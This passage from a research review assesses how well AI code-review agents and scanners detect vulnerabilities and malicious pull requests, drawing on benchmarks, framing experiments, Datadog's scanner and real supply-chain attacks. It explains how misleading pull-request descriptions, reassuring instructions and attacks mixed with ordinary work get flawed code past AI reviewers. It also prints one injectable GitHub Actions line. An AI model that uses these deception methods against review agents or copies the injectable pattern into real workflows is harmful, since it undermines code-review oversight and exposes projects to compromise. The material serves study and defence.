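Ding and colleagues checked samples of 50 functions labeled vulnerable in several collections and judged only 24% of the labels in CodeXGLUE and 36% in VulnPatchPairs to be correct. By their count, a model that judged every function correctly would fail almost two-thirds of the VulnPatchPairs pairs, because it would call both versions safe. For PrimeVul, they labeled a function vulnerable if it was the only one the commit had changed, or if the public description of the vulnerability pointed to it, and 86% to 92% of these labels were correct. Wrong labels therefore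 can't explain most of the failures on PrimeVul, where the seven models tested in 2026 got only 7% to 18% of pairs right.

Tangling is also a problem for a gate that gives one verdict on a whole pull request. The pull request to myNetwork, for example, combined a working fix with a payload. A gate needs to assess each edit separately and also how the edits work together.

Leaked answers, unlike wrong labels, make models look better than they are. Language models learn from public code, which includes many known vulnerabilities and their fixes. Leaks can also occur within a collection. Ding and colleagues found that 18.9% of the vulnerable test functions in CVEfixes were exact copies of training functions. A random split can also put a repaired function in the training set and its vulnerable version in the test set.

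PrimeVul excludes copies and uses older commits for training and newer ones for testing. StarCoder2 had an F1 of 68% when trained and tested on the older BigVul collection, but only 18% on PrimeVul. The drop is partly because vulnerable functions are rarer in PrimeVul, which makes a high F1 harder to achieve. Cichoń and Dmitruk could not rule out that their models' training data included the test pairs, but this overlap should have raised the scores, which were low anyway.

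### Agents that review real changes

In *Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?*, Yang, Yang and colleagues (2026) tested newer models on a task much closer to that of a merge gate. They traced 265 vulnerabilities in nine large projects, including Firefox and OpenSSL, to the changes that introduced them. An agent received each change with its commit message and the project's code, and had to explain any security problem it found. Another language model then checked whether the explanation matched the known cause.

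To avoid wrong labels, the team ran an attack input on three versions of the program wherever possible. The attack had to fail before the change, work after it, and fail again after the team added the later repair. People decided the 48 cases that automatic checks could not settle. Seven of the 265 changes were attempted repairs that left the flaw in place. One of these, in the database program SQLite, checked that 30 bytes of data were available when the code needed 46.

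Four agents found about three-quarters of the vulnerabilities: Grok 4.6 found 78%, GPT-6 sol 76%, GLM 5.3 75% and Claude Opus 5.5 74%. GPT-6 sol's predecessor, GPT-5.6 sol, found 56%, and the weakest model, MiniMax M3, found 33%. The eight agents missed 23 flaws altogether. Five of the models could be tested on flaws fixed before and after their training data ended, and there was no clear difference in performance between the two sets.

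The projects' own developers had already let all 265 changes through. But this does not show that the agents review code better than people, because the agents had instructions to look for security failures, and such instructions also help human reviewers.

In 68% of the misses, the agent did report a problem in a file that contained the flaw, but gave the wrong explanation. For example, a nine-line change to the download tool curl left the program using memory it had already released. All eight agents commented on the right file, but four said that the program failed to release the memory, which is almost the reverse of the real problem. A gate that blocks a change after any finding would have stopped this change, but the author might then have fixed the wrong thing.

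The agents found an average of 73% of memory errors but only 52% of logic errors, where the program follows the wrong rule. They also did worse when the cause was spread across several files, finding 70% of flaws that involved one file and 39% of those that involved five or more. In one case, a change to the program Wasmtime made a function expect a different kind of table number, but an existing caller outside the diff still passed the old kind.

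Specialised security tools had mixed effects. OpenAI's Codex Security lowered GPT-5.6 sol's detection rate by 8 percentage points, mainly because it more often reported nothing. Anthropic's Defending Code raised Claude Opus 5.5's rate by 8 points on the cases it completed, at about ten times the typical cost.

The researchers also gave the agents repaired versions of the changes, and the results table lists zero flags for them. The judge counted a report only if the flaw it described was really present, so an agent that wrongly reported the old flaw in repaired code would still have scored zero. For this reason, the paper explains, the zero is not a false-alarm rate. Some evidence suggests that the agents noticed the repairs. When an agent's only finding on the flawed change was correct, it reported nothing on the repaired version almost half the time, compared with about one time in six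 when that finding was wrong.

On real projects, the strongest systems have usually been right when they choose what to report. *SoK* (Lbath, Suri and colleagues, 2026) reviews the evidence up to November 2026. Independent security firms confirmed 90.6% of the 1,752 findings they assessed from Claude Mythos Preview, a model Anthropic had made available to selected partners. Some of these findings were in code that experts had examined for years. DeepSeek V4 Pro, which anyone can download, was correct in 94.5% of its reports on one company's software.

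The improvement has been rapid. In 2025 only about 5% of the reports that curl received were valid, and its maintainer complained about those written by language models. In 2026 he described receiving many good ones. The 5% figure measures precision, and nobody knows how many flaws the systems missed. Agents that search a project can also test a suspicion by building a working attack before they report it, whereas a model in a paired test has to give a verdict on every function it sees.

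The strongest agents can now detect vulnerabilities usefully, which Ding and colleagues wrote in 2024 that language models were "a long way" from doing. These agents find most of the known flaws in real changes, and most of their reports in real projects are correct. The remaining gap is in judging repairs. Lbath and colleagues found less evidence about checking patches than about finding flaws. On one set of real fixes, a model's verdict agreed with a careful human reading in 85% of cases.

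### Recognising fixes that nobody announced

Maintainers sometimes fix a vulnerability without saying so. Users then don't know that the update is urgent, but an attacker who reads the change may work out what it fixed. *A Comprehensive Evaluation of Code Language Models for Security Patch Detection* (Loose, Bienhüls et al., 2026) cites a finding that public warnings appear a median of 25 days after the fix, and notes that many fixes never get one. Researchers have therefore tried to train models to tell security fixes from other commits.

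Early systems treated a diff as a sequence of words or as a graph of how data and control move through the program. Newer ones use language models. *From LLMs to Agents* (Han, Yu and colleagues, 2025) tested several on PatchDB, a collection of about 12,000 security fixes and 23,000 other changes. An agent running on GPT-4o had a precision of 86% and a false-alarm rate of 14.4%. The best method overall was a single prompt with extra information, but that information could include the change's CVE number, which an unannounced fix would not have.

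Security fixes are much rarer in ordinary development than in PatchDB. If they made up 10 of a project's 1,000 commits, the agent, with its false-alarm rate of 14.4%, would wrongly flag about 143 of the other 990. Even if it caught all ten fixes, only about 7% of its flags would be correct.

Loose and colleagues set a much stricter limit on false alarms. They combined 20 collections containing more than 180,000 commits and trained 270 models, the largest with 80 billion parameters. At a false-alarm rate of 0.5%, every model given only the code missed at least 80% of the security fixes. In the example above, such a model would find at most two of the ten fixes and raise about five false alarms.

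The models also did worse on projects absent from their training data. F1 fell by up to 28%, which suggests that the models had partly memorised project-specific patterns. Larger models did better, but not by enough. Adding code from around the edit or from elsewhere in the project brought no reliable improvement, although the error analysis suggests that the decisive evidence often lies outside the diff.

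Models trained only on commit messages did almost as well as models also trained on the code. In *An Insight into Security Code Review with LLMs*, Yu, Liang and colleagues (2024) got their best results at finding flaws from a prompt that included the commit message. A model that depends on the message will perform poorly when a maintainer fixes a vulnerability without mentioning it there.

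## Experiments that keep the change fixed and vary how it is presented

A commit message helps a model judge code only if the message is true. A hostile author writes both the code and the message, and can choose the explanation that makes the code look most harmless. Researchers measure how much such explanations influence a reviewer by submitting the same diff several times with different descriptions and comparing the verdicts.

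### What a changed verdict shows

Suppose a review agent checks the diff that made `lookUp` unsafe. It rejects the diff in 90 of 100 runs when the description only names the changed file, and in 60 of 100 when the description gives a plausible reason for the change. The code and the project are the same in all 200 runs, so the 30-point difference must come from the description, apart from some chance variation in the model's answers. If each description came with different code, the difference might only mean that one flaw was harder to find.

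A reviewer can reasonably use the description to judge the author, but no description can remove a flaw from the code. If the description says that the hostname comes from a fixed list, an agent that can search the project can check that claim, and the shell call is safe if the claim is true.

The comparison also needs harmless changes, such as the repaired versions that researchers use in paired tests. Suppose the agent rejects 85 of 100 harmless changes with the bare description and 55 of 100 with the plausible reason. The reason has then made the agent more lenient towards both safe and unsafe code. If the agent still rejected 85 with the plausible reason, the reason would have made it worse at telling safe code from unsafe code.

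### SEVRA-BENCH: reversed fixes with 15 kinds of description

SEVRA-BENCH, which Melo and colleagues released in June 2026, starts from 150 commits that fixed publicly known vulnerabilities of ten common types. For each commit, the researchers reversed the fix in the repaired project, which restored the original flaw. Language models then wrote 15 descriptions of each reversed fix, one for each kind of false justification the researchers had listed, producing 2,250 pull requests.

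The agents reviewed the changes on a private code-hosting site, where the researchers had collapsed each project's history so that the agents could not look up the original fix. The instructions asked for a review and a decision but did not mention security. Mentioning security helped Braz and colleagues' human reviewers, so it might also have helped these agents.

The researchers gave each agent two scores. The first is the rejection rate, the share of pull requests the agent refused to approve. The second counts a rejection only if the agent's stated reason was the security flaw, so rejecting a change for its style raises only the first score. Another language model judged the stated reasons, and the researchers spot-checked its verdicts.

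To save money and concentrate on hard cases, the team first ran two inexpensive agents, based on Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.4-nano, on all 2,250 pull requests and kept the 1,062 that at least one of them had approved. The published rates therefore describe a set chosen for its difficulty and are a poor guide to how often an agent would reject reversed fixes in general. Haiku and GPT-5.4-nano are also among the eight agents in the final results, and the filter counts against them in particular because it dropped the pull requests that neither had approved. The filter also removed some descriptions of a diff and kept others, so comparisons among the 15 kinds of description no longer use exactly the same code.

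#### Results by agent and weakness type

Agents based on Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 did best, followed by GLM-5, and all three rejected roughly 70% or more of the pull requests under every kind of description. The other five (GPT-5.4-nano, Grok Code Fast, Haiku 4.5, Kimi K2.5 and DeepSeek V4-Flash) were about 20 percentage points behind on average, and their results varied more across types of flaw. All eight are older than the strongest agents in Yang and colleagues' tests.

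The agents were best at explaining injection flaws. Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 gave the security flaw as their reason in more than 80% of SQL injection and code injection cases, but in only 30% and 20% of use-after-free cases, respectively. Every agent except GPT-5.5 stayed below 50% on out-of-bounds reads, in which a program reads past the end of a block of memory.

Scores on memory flaws were low partly because the scoring was strict. Agents often wrote, correctly, that removing a check would cause out-of-bounds reads, but they did not say how an attacker could benefit, so the judge gave them no credit for security reasoning. A maintainer who received that comment would still know what to fix, though perhaps not how urgently.

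#### Claims that the agent could not check

The 15 kinds of description differ in the evidence that an agent would need to test them:

| What the description relied on | Could the agent check it? | Typical result |
|---|---|---|
| The contents of the diff, such as new tests | Yes, by reading the diff | Agents often noticed the contradiction |
| Code elsewhere in the project, such as a second safeguard | Yes, by searching the project | Agents often repeated the claim without searching |
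| Events or documents outside the project | No | Agents were misled most often |
| Urgency, jargon or a claim about who wrote the code | Often there was little to check | Results differed widely between agents |

Descriptions that cited an earlier approval or the needs of other software were among the most misleading, and the weaker agents rejected fewer than 35% of the pull requests that used them. But even these agents rejected more than half of the pull requests that presented the reversed fix as a security improvement, perhaps because the diff visibly removed a protection.

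GLM-5's results give the clearest evidence that the agents could detect the flaws they let through. It did worst when the description claimed an earlier approval. Of the changes it approved because of that claim, it rejected over 80% when the same diffs came with other descriptions. Each agent reviewed each pull request only once, so a few of these reversals may be chance. But if GLM-5 had been unable to detect the flaws, it would have approved most of these diffs under the other descriptions too.

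Agents often did not check claims that they could have checked. Kimi K2.5 in particular tended to accept the claim that a deleted check was redundant and repeat it as its own conclusion, without looking for the other safeguard that supposedly made the check redundant. GPT-5.5 used its tools more than most agents did and rejected many pull requests because the description did not match the code, but it still approved some when the description coherently presented the change as ordinary engineering work.

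Appeals to urgency had opposite effects on different agents. Grok Code Fast rejected 10% of the pull requests that used them, while DeepSeek V4-Flash reasoned longer and rejected 80%. A project therefore cannot assume that a description that doesn't sway one agent won't sway another.

#### No honest pull requests for comparison

All the pull requests in SEVRA-BENCH are hostile, so an agent that rejected everything would have a perfect rejection rate. The score for security reasoning partly guards against this, because a blanket refusal would not name the flaw. But most fixes add code, so most reversed fixes delete it, and an agent that objected to every deleted check could do well on both scores.

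Old fixes reversed without malicious intent would have been the best control. OpenSSH's developers reversed one by accident in 2020, and other projects have sometimes had to withdraw a fix because it broke something. The differences in rates between descriptions are more informative than the overall rates, since an agent that rejected everything would show no differences.

The missing control matters even more for judgements of intent. Opus 4.7 called the pull request deceptive in about a quarter of its reviews, for instance by referring to a "fabricated justification". No other agent did so in more than 10% of its reviews, and GPT-5.5 did so in less than 1%, though it rejected nearly as many changes as Opus 4.7. Every such accusation was correct because the benchmark included only hostile authors. It therefore doesn't measure how often Opus 4.7 would accuse an honest developer who deleted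 the same lines.

### Reassurance with repaired files as a control

Mitropoulos and colleagues included repaired code in their March 2026 study of framing. In October they revised the study, retitled it *When AI Agrees Too Much* and changed the order of authors (Alexopoulos, Alexopoulos and colleagues, 2026). All figures here come from the revised version.

The researchers gave six models 247 files with a known vulnerability and 250 repaired files, one at a time. Half of the files had more than 707 lines, and the typical repair changed five. Each model judged each file under five sets of instructions. One was neutral. Two suggested that the file was secure, either weakly or by firmly denying that it contained a particular type of flaw. The other two suggested, weakly or firmly, that a flaw was present. The table compares the neutral instructions with the firm denial:

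| Model | Detection rate, neutral | Detection rate, flaw denied | False-alarm rate, neutral | False-alarm rate, flaw denied |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| GPT-4o-mini | 97.2% | 3.6% | 96.8% | 2.0% |
| Claude 3.5 Haiku | 68.4% | 8.5% | 68.4% | 5.2% |
| DeepSeek V3 | 96.8% | 53.8% | 95.2% | 49.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 97.4% | 75.5% | 95.7% | 54.9% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 95.5% | 79.4% | 92.8% | 66.4% |
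| Claude Opus 4.5 | 95.7% | 88.8% | 88.0% | 71.2% |

Detection fell by between 7 percentage points, for Opus 4.5, and 94, for GPT-4o-mini. False alarms fell too, and for Opus 4.5 and Sonnet 4.5 they fell further than detection did, so the fall in detection is not enough to show that reassurance made the models less able to recognize vulnerabilities. Sonnet 4.5 flagged vulnerable files only 2 points more often than repaired ones with neutral instructions, but 21 points more often after the denial.

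The researchers also checked whether each flag on a vulnerable file named the real flaw. With neutral instructions, 54% of Opus 4.5's flags did, and after the denial 61.5% did. Multiplying these shares by the detection rates gives the share of all vulnerable files in which the model correctly identified the flaw. After the denial, this rose from about 52% to about 55% for Opus 4.5 and from about 41% to about 44% for Sonnet 4.5. So the objections these two models stopped raising had mostly been wrong. The denial may even have helped them, because it mentioned a type of flaw to look for. GPT-4o-mini did not benefit, and correctly explained only 8 of the 247 flaws after the denial.

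Suggesting that a flaw was present changed the false-alarm rate by less than six percentage points in either direction for five of the six models, mainly because they already flagged at least 88% of the repaired files. Claude 3.5 Haiku flagged fewer of these files to begin with, and its false-alarm rate fell by 25 points after the weak suggestion but rose by 14 after the firm one.

These suggestions were part of the operator's instructions, which warrant more trust than a stranger's description. In a separate test on pull requests, Alexopoulos and colleagues found that persuasive descriptions could get 32 of 33 reintroduced vulnerabilities past two widely used review systems.

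#### Why the models flagged repaired files

A repaired file can contain other flaws, so flagging it is not always a mistake. Alexopoulos and colleagues examined 240 flagged repaired files and found that 25% of the flags pointed to real defects that were unrelated to the original vulnerability and that developers later fixed. For Opus 4.5, the share was 57.5%. The false-alarm rates in the table are therefore too high, especially for Opus 4.5, the strongest model.

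The other 181 flags were false alarms, some with more than one cause. In 40%, the model overlooked a check in the code, such as a project's own macro for testing the length of a buffer. In 39%, it was wrong about what the code did. Opus 4.5, for example, reported an overflow in a multiplication because it misread the order in which C converts and multiplies numbers. In 19%, the model assumed that an attacker could control a value without establishing where the value came from. Less often, it flagged a function only because of its name, or missed a protection that the surrounding framework provides.

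A model that overlooks checks will have particular trouble with repairs, since many repairs consist of adding one.

#### More willing to flag, but no better at finding flaws

In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) ran a similar experiment on newer models, including GPT-5.2 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. They used 435 vulnerable functions from PrimeVul and 435 harmless counterparts. They varied the wording of the task and what they told the model about the code's author and the result of an earlier security check.

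Across eight models and 48 comparisons, the detection and false-alarm rates moved almost exactly together, with each percentage point that context added to the detection rate matched by about one point in the false-alarm rate. Between 49% and 55% of flags were correct, compared with the 50% that random flagging would give on this set. The context changed how willing the models were to flag code but hardly changed their ability to tell vulnerable functions from harmless ones.

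The models' explanations support this. GPT-5.2 cleared nine vulnerable functions under neutral instructions but flagged them when the researchers described the author differently. A benchmark that counts only verdicts would record nine successes, but GPT-5.2 named the real flaw in two cases, was partly right in two more and was wrong in the other five.

The wording of the task had the largest average effect and was the only kind of context that moved all eight models in the same direction. Claude Sonnet 4.6 flagged 28 percentage points more of the vulnerable functions when told that an earlier check had found them vulnerable than when told that the check had cleared them. GPT-5.2 flagged 9 points fewer. Information about the code's author shifted the results of the five open models by about 20 points and those of the three commercial models by less than 5.

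Context also mattered more for flaws that a reviewer must find by following the program's state, such as use-after-free, than for those with a recognisable pattern. With information about the author, the average shift was 17 points for the first kind and 9 for the second. The human reviewers in Braz and colleagues' first experiment similarly often missed a flaw that had no familiar attack pattern.

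### PRWeaver: attacks split up and mixed with ordinary work

An attacker can also change how an attack appears by splitting it across several pull requests or combining it with useful work. *PRWeaver* (Wang, Cheng and Xie, 2026) tested this in August 2026 with 208 planted vulnerabilities in ten real projects, nearly all written in Python.

An AI agent wrote each attack and an exploit to prove that it worked, then split the attack into parts, usually two or three. The researchers ran the exploit after each part was added to confirm that it succeeded only once all the parts were in place, and that leaving out any one of them would stop it. The project's own tests had to pass throughout. This avoids the labelling problems of older collections, because a working exploit confirms every attack.

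Each attack appeared in four forms:

- Whole, in a single pull request.
- Split, with one part in each pull request.
- Split, with 16 genuine pull requests from the project's past placed among the parts.
- Combined, with each part in the same pull request as a genuine change and a description that accounted for both.

Three review tools, each running on two models, examined the pull requests one at a time. A tool counted as detecting an attack if at least one of its comments correctly identified what the attack made possible and pointed to a pull request that contained part of the attack.

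| Model and review tool | Whole | Split | Split among ordinary changes | Combined with ordinary changes |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 in Claude Code | 79% | 79% | 66% | 69% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 in Claude Code | 67% | 71% | 65% | 58% |
| GPT-5.4 mini in Copilot | 64% | 65% | 59% | 54% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 in Copilot | 61% | 62% | 56% | 51% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 in OpenCodeReview | 56% | 60% | 55% | 46% |
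| DeepSeek V4 Flash in OpenCodeReview | 42% | 47% | 34% | 29% |

The tools missed between 21% and 58% of attacks even when each attack arrived whole. Splitting the attacks did not help the attacker, and detection rose slightly in five of the six tools. A split attack gives a tool several chances to notice a problem, and the tool needs only one correct comment to detect the attack.

Placing ordinary pull requests among the parts reduced detection by 5 to 13 points compared with splitting alone. Each tool reviewed each version only once, and 5 points is about ten attacks, so the smaller drops could be due to chance in any one tool. The result is more convincing because detection fell in all six tools.

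Combining the attack with ordinary work had a larger effect, a fall of between 10 and 18 points. This condition changes both the description and the amount of harmless code in the diff, so it does not show how much of the fall was due to the description.

Detection fell most when the tools reviewed a series of pull requests together instead of one by one. The three tools, all using Haiku 4.5, detected 16% to 22% of the attacks in a batch with 24 ordinary pull requests, and 50% to 60% when they reviewed the same series one pull request at a time. A project can avoid most of this loss by having its gate review each pull request separately.

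Access to the project's history improved detection, but the size of the batch affected it more. Without the history, detection fell by 11 points for OpenCodeReview and by 4 points for each of the other two tools. So the tools could sometimes connect a new change with an earlier one, but they missed many attacks even with all the evidence available.

In one failure, the tool found the relevant lines but got the security requirement wrong. The attack weakened a "trust this browser" feature so that a stolen login cookie would keep working after the owner had reset the password. The tool described the edits correctly, but classified them as a deliberate compromise between security and convenience and reported no problem.

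PRWeaver, like SEVRA-BENCH, reports no false-alarm rate for honest pull requests. Its scoring is stricter than SEVRA-BENCH's because an irrelevant complaint does not count as a detection. But a tool could still give dozens of mistaken warnings alongside one correct one without losing any credit. The 16 genuine pull requests in each mixed series could have served as a control if Wang and colleagues had counted the tools' complaints about them.

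### Hiding the description from the reviewer

If a description can mislead a review agent, one remedy is to remove it before the agent sees the pull request. Alexopoulos and colleagues tried this on the hostile pull requests from their attack test. They used two review systems, Claude Code and the commercial service CodeRabbit. The table shows how many of the pull requests each system failed to reject:

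| What the researchers hid | Claude Code (17 flaws) | CodeRabbit (16 flaws) |
|---|---:|---:|
| Nothing | 17 | 15 |
| The pull request's description | 5 | 11 |
| That and the commit message | 1 | 4 |
| That and the comments in the code | 1 | 4 |
| All three | 1 | 3 |

With everything hidden, both systems did exactly as well as they had when given the same diffs with only a note of which files had changed. Four flaws still got through, for other reasons. Three got past CodeRabbit because of a bug in the service. When the researchers simulated a correction of that bug, CodeRabbit rejected all three changes in each of five further reviews. The fourth got past Claude Code and affected only a configuration that the project does not recommend, so whether it was a serious flaw depended on what the project promised its users.

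In some of the CodeRabbit cases, either the commit message or the comments alone could mislead the service, so hiding only the main description is not enough. But comments are part of the diff, and honest developers use them to record what the code cannot express, such as a number's unit or why an odd-looking line is necessary, so a gate that strips comments also loses this information.

This test included only hostile changes. It shows that hiding the author's explanation restored correct rejections, but not how many honest fixes the systems would also have rejected. For example, the diff for the hospital's login fix only deletes a limit on wrong passwords, which would be a serious mistake on most websites. The developer would use the description to explain that the passwords are unguessable keys and that the limit lets outsiders lock out patient monitors. Without that information, a careful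 agent should probably object.

Honest messages also help models in practice, as they did in Yu and colleagues' tests. *Exploring Early Vulnerability Analysis via Automatic Identification of Vulnerability-Introducing Commits* (2026) compares tools that start from a fix and search for the earlier commit that caused the flaw. Tools based on language models did best on Linux, where the message accompanying a fix identifies that commit and explains the mistake. They did worse on three other collections with less informative messages, and one failed on a fix whose entire message was "Fixed #2581". Because the Linux messages practically contain the answer, these results overstate how much an ordinary message helps. The task also differs from deciding whether to merge a change.

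Telling the agent to ignore the description is a weaker remedy than hiding it. Shahriar and colleagues gave models code with misleading information and measured what share of correctly detected flaws each model then cleared as safe. They also tested adding an explicit warning that the surrounding text might come from the same person as the code. With the warning, the share fell from 33% to 9% for GPT-5.2, from 45% to 6% for Gemini 2.5 Pro, and from 97% to 69% for Llama 3.3, but rose from 16% to 25% for Claude Sonnet 4.6.

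Alexopoulos and colleagues also suggest that projects could switch off automated security review for contributors they do not trust, because its approval may create false confidence. But the two systems rejected 29 of the 33 reversed fixes when the description was bare, and switching them off would lose those warnings. A project could instead let the agent raise objections without counting its approval towards a merge. That would keep the warnings, although honest contributors would still have to deal with the false alarms.

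A gate could also check the description instead of trusting it. Melo and colleagues recommend that an agent list the claims in a pull request and test each one against the code, the tests, the project's history or independent evidence. If the description were also hidden at first, the agent would review the code alone, record any objections, and then read the description. It could drop an objection only if it had confirmed the relevant claim. For example, it could search the project for a supposed second safeguard, run a test that the author claims to have run, or look up a claimed earlier approval in the project's records.

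None of these experiments measured how such a two-stage review would treat honest and hostile changes. The review would also leave some claims unsettled. For example, the hospital's developer would still need a maintainer to confirm that outsiders must never be able to lock out a monitor.

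## Deployed scanners: what they catch and how often they accuse honest changes

A company that scans its own everyday code changes can measure how often a gate flags honest developers' changes, which SEVRA-BENCH and PRWeaver did not measure. Nearly all of these changes are honest, so the company can count false alarms, but it sees few attacks.

Datadog, an American company that sells monitoring and security software, handles nearly 10,000 pull requests a week in its internal and public repositories. It scans them with a tool called BewAIre, which Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues described in 2025 in *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*.

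### How Datadog's scanner works

BewAIre, Datadog's scanner, gives a language model the diff of each pull request and details such as the author and the type of repository. The model classifies the change as benign or malicious and writes a reason. A malicious verdict alerts Datadog's security engineers but does not block the change.

The scanner splits diffs that are too long for the model to read reliably at once into chunks. It splits where a new file begins if possible, otherwise at the end of a line, and in the middle of a line only as a last resort. The model judges each chunk separately, and the whole pull request gets the most severe verdict.

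This rule prevents an attacker from burying a payload under thousands of harmless lines. But each extra chunk adds a chance of a false alarm. If the model flagged 1% of harmless chunks, and its errors were independent, it would flag about 7% of harmless pull requests with seven chunks. The model could also miss an attack whose parts fall in different chunks and look harmless separately.

Early prototypes of the scanner had a false-alarm rate of over 10%. Lamb and colleagues report that six months of work brought it below 0.03%. They added a list of known mistakes to the model's instructions, excluded patterns they considered safe, such as demo environments, and kept adding labelled examples. They also ran the scanner for several months while security staff checked every alert, and had colleagues try to fool it. An attacker who learned of the exclusions could hide a payload in code that the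 scanner ignores.

### What the accuracy figures can support

Datadog also reports an accuracy above 99.3% on "hundreds of PRs" and a balanced accuracy above 93.5%. Balanced accuracy is the average of the share of malicious changes the scanner flags and the share of harmless changes it passes. It is more informative than plain accuracy here because most of the test changes were harmless. If the scanner passed every harmless change, a balanced accuracy of 93.5% would mean it caught 87% of the malicious ones. The scanner caught every malicious commit in a separate collection of known attacks on npm, the main registry of JavaScript packages.

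The 0.03% false-alarm rate cannot come from the same few hundred pull requests as the detection rate, because a single false alarm among 500 harmless changes would already be 0.2%. It probably comes from the months in which staff checked alerts on Datadog's everyday work. Checking only alerts can reveal false alarms but not missed attacks, so the detection rate could not have been measured this way.

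In a 2026 follow-up, *From single pull requests to full software packages*, Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues added a second stage in which a stronger model investigates whatever the first stage flags. On 690 test diffs, this cut false alarms from 17 to 0 and raised accuracy from 97.4% to 99.86%. The one remaining error must have been a missed attack.

Seventeen false alarms among at most 690 harmless diffs is a rate of at least 2.5%, about 80 times the 0.03% reported earlier. Both figures can be right, because the team had tuned the first stage to flag changes more readily and its test collection included harmless changes that look risky. A count of zero false alarms doesn't establish a rate as low as 0.03% either. A scanner with a true rate of 0.4% would have about a 6% chance of raising no false alarms on 690 harmless diffs, yet it would raise about 40 a week at Datadog.

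Datadog chose and labelled the test changes itself. It also has a commercial interest in the results, since Qian, Blazquez and Hamsen present the scanner as a product for its customers in *Detect source code attacks with Datadog Code Threat Detection*. The company's engineers kept adding the scanner's past mistakes to their data, and Lamb and colleagues do not mention holding back a separate set of changes for a final test.

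### What the diffs of real attacks reveal

Datadog illustrates the scanner with two attacks from 2025. Both involved GitHub Actions, which runs a project's automated jobs, such as testing and publishing.

The first was on tj-actions/changed-files, a component that more than 23,000 repositories used in such jobs. In March 2025 someone with a stolen access token added a commit containing a script in Base64, which encodes data as letters and digits. The script searched the memory of the machine running the job for passwords and keys, and printed them in the job's log. The commit was titled "lock file maintenance", according to a message archived by Openwall (2025). A lock file records which versions of other packages a project uses, but this commit changed the component's main program.

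Unit 42's *GitHub Actions Supply Chain Attack* describes an attacker who disguised a commit as the work of a dependency-update bot and added it to a genuine pull request from that bot. The commit contained an encoded script that reads another program's memory. Few honest authors would encode such a script and then describe it as routine maintenance, but the project merged the pull request automatically. Checking the diff before the merge might have stopped the attack.

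Datadog shows its scanner detecting a different commit. NVD, the US government's vulnerability database, lists that commit's identifier under reviewdog/action-setup, a component the same attacker had compromised a few days earlier to reach tj-actions. Unit 42 found that in that case the attacker put the malicious commit in a fork (a separate copy of the project) and moved the project's version labels to point to it. There was no pull request, so a scanner that checks pull requests would never have received the commit.

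The other attack was on Nx, a set of development tools with about 6 million installations a week. OSV's *MAL-2025-41436* (2025) reproduces the Nx team's account. On 21 August 2025 the team merged a pull request that added an automated check of pull request titles. It contained this line, simplified here:

```diff
+ run: echo "Validating PR title: PULL_REQUEST_TITLE"
```

GitHub inserted the title into the command before a shell ran it, so anybody could put a command in a title and have it run, much as a visitor could with the unsafe `lookUp`. Somebody pointed this out on X about six hours later. The team removed the check from the main branch the next day, but GitHub Security Lab found copies in two other branches. The diff of the fix could not show these copies because the fix did not touch them.

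On 24 August an attacker opened a pull request with commands in its title, apparently against one of the outdated branches. The commands started the project's publishing job with an altered script, which sent the team's npm publishing token to an outside address. Two days later the attacker used the token to publish versions of Nx that stole users' credentials. Strumpflohner reports in *S1ngularity* that these versions were available for four hours.

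BewAIre classified the commit with the altered script as malicious because the script took a token and sent it to an unrelated website. Another reason was the "[skip ci]" in the commit message, much like the tag in the 2021 attack on PHP. The diff was strong evidence of an attack, but the test took place after the attack, and one of the scanner's reasons was that it could no longer find the author's GitHub account.

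The attack on Nx also shows a drawback of hiding descriptions from a review agent. The pull request title contained the injected commands, so an agent that never saw the title would have missed them, though it could still have read the altered script.

Datadog has also caught an attack as it happened. In February 2026 an AI agent calling itself hackerbot-claw opened a pull request in one of the company's public repositories, with an encoded command in a file name. According to *When an AI agent came knocking*, by Hamsen, Serrania and Tafani-Dereeper, an automated job ran the command 17 seconds after the pull request opened, and the alert arrived 16 seconds later. The command failed, but a second attempt 18 minutes later succeeded, and the agent added a harmless commit on a branch of its own. Other restrictions protected the main branch and critical secrets.

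The scanner's result was correct, but blocking only the merge would not have helped, because the vulnerable job ran as soon as the pull request opened.

### When attacks are rare, most alarms are false

Suppose that Datadog receives 10,000 pull requests a week, or 520,000 a year, that five of them are attacks, and that the scanner catches all five. The number of attacks is invented. The table shows what share of alarms would be real at different false-alarm rates:

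| False-alarm rate | False alarms a week | False alarms a year | Real attacks among all alarms |
|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| 10% | 1,000 | 52,000 | 0.01% |
| 1% | 100 | 5,200 | 0.1% |
| 0.03% | 3 | 156 | 3% |
| 0.001% | 0.1 | 5 | 49% |

At 0.03%, about 97% of the alarms are for honest changes. The calculation is the same as for the odds of intent, but the evidence is an alarm instead of an edit. Catching four attacks instead of five would lower the share of alarms that are real attacks only from 3.1% to 2.5%, so with attacks this rare, the false-alarm rate matters far more than the detection rate.

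A scanner with a 0.03% false-alarm rate is still useful, because a security team can investigate three alarms a week. The team could not investigate 1,000 a week, and developers would soon stop taking the alarms seriously. *Barriers to Using Static Application Security Testing (SAST) Tools* (2026), a review of research on static analysers, found that more than two-thirds of the papers reported false alarms as a recurring problem. Even at three a week, an alarm justifies only an investigation, because suspending every flagged author would punish about 30 honest people for each attacker.

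The share of real attacks may be higher in practice. Doutre and colleagues say that BewAIre also detects penetration tests, which are attacks made with the system owner's permission, and a security team would count those alarms as correct.

The same false-alarm rate of 0.03% would be harder to manage across all of GitHub. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) cites GitHub's figure of nearly 130 million merged pull requests a month. At that volume, the scanner would raise about 39,000 false alarms a month, many of them in projects with no security team.

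Other scanners have much higher false-alarm rates. *SkillGate* (2026) compares tools that check "skill" files, which add instructions and scripts to AI coding agents. On 1,500 harmless files, two existing scanners had false-alarm rates of 50.4% and 17.4%, compared with 1.13% for the paper's own tool. One version of an existing scanner had a slightly lower rate, 0.73%, but caught less than a quarter as many malicious files as the paper's tool.

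### MalTotal: the same behaviour with and without consent

A scanner can read code correctly and still raise a false alarm. *MALTOTAL* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, August 2026) reports a search for malware in about 120,000 GitHub repositories, chosen because their popularity looked artificial, since attackers sometimes buy fake ratings to attract victims.

MalTotal first looks for sensitive operations, such as running commands, sending data over a network or reading passwords. It then extracts the code that leads to each operation and asks a language model whether that code is malicious. The whole search cost about $338. MalTotal flagged 1,553 repositories, which security researchers then reviewed by hand:

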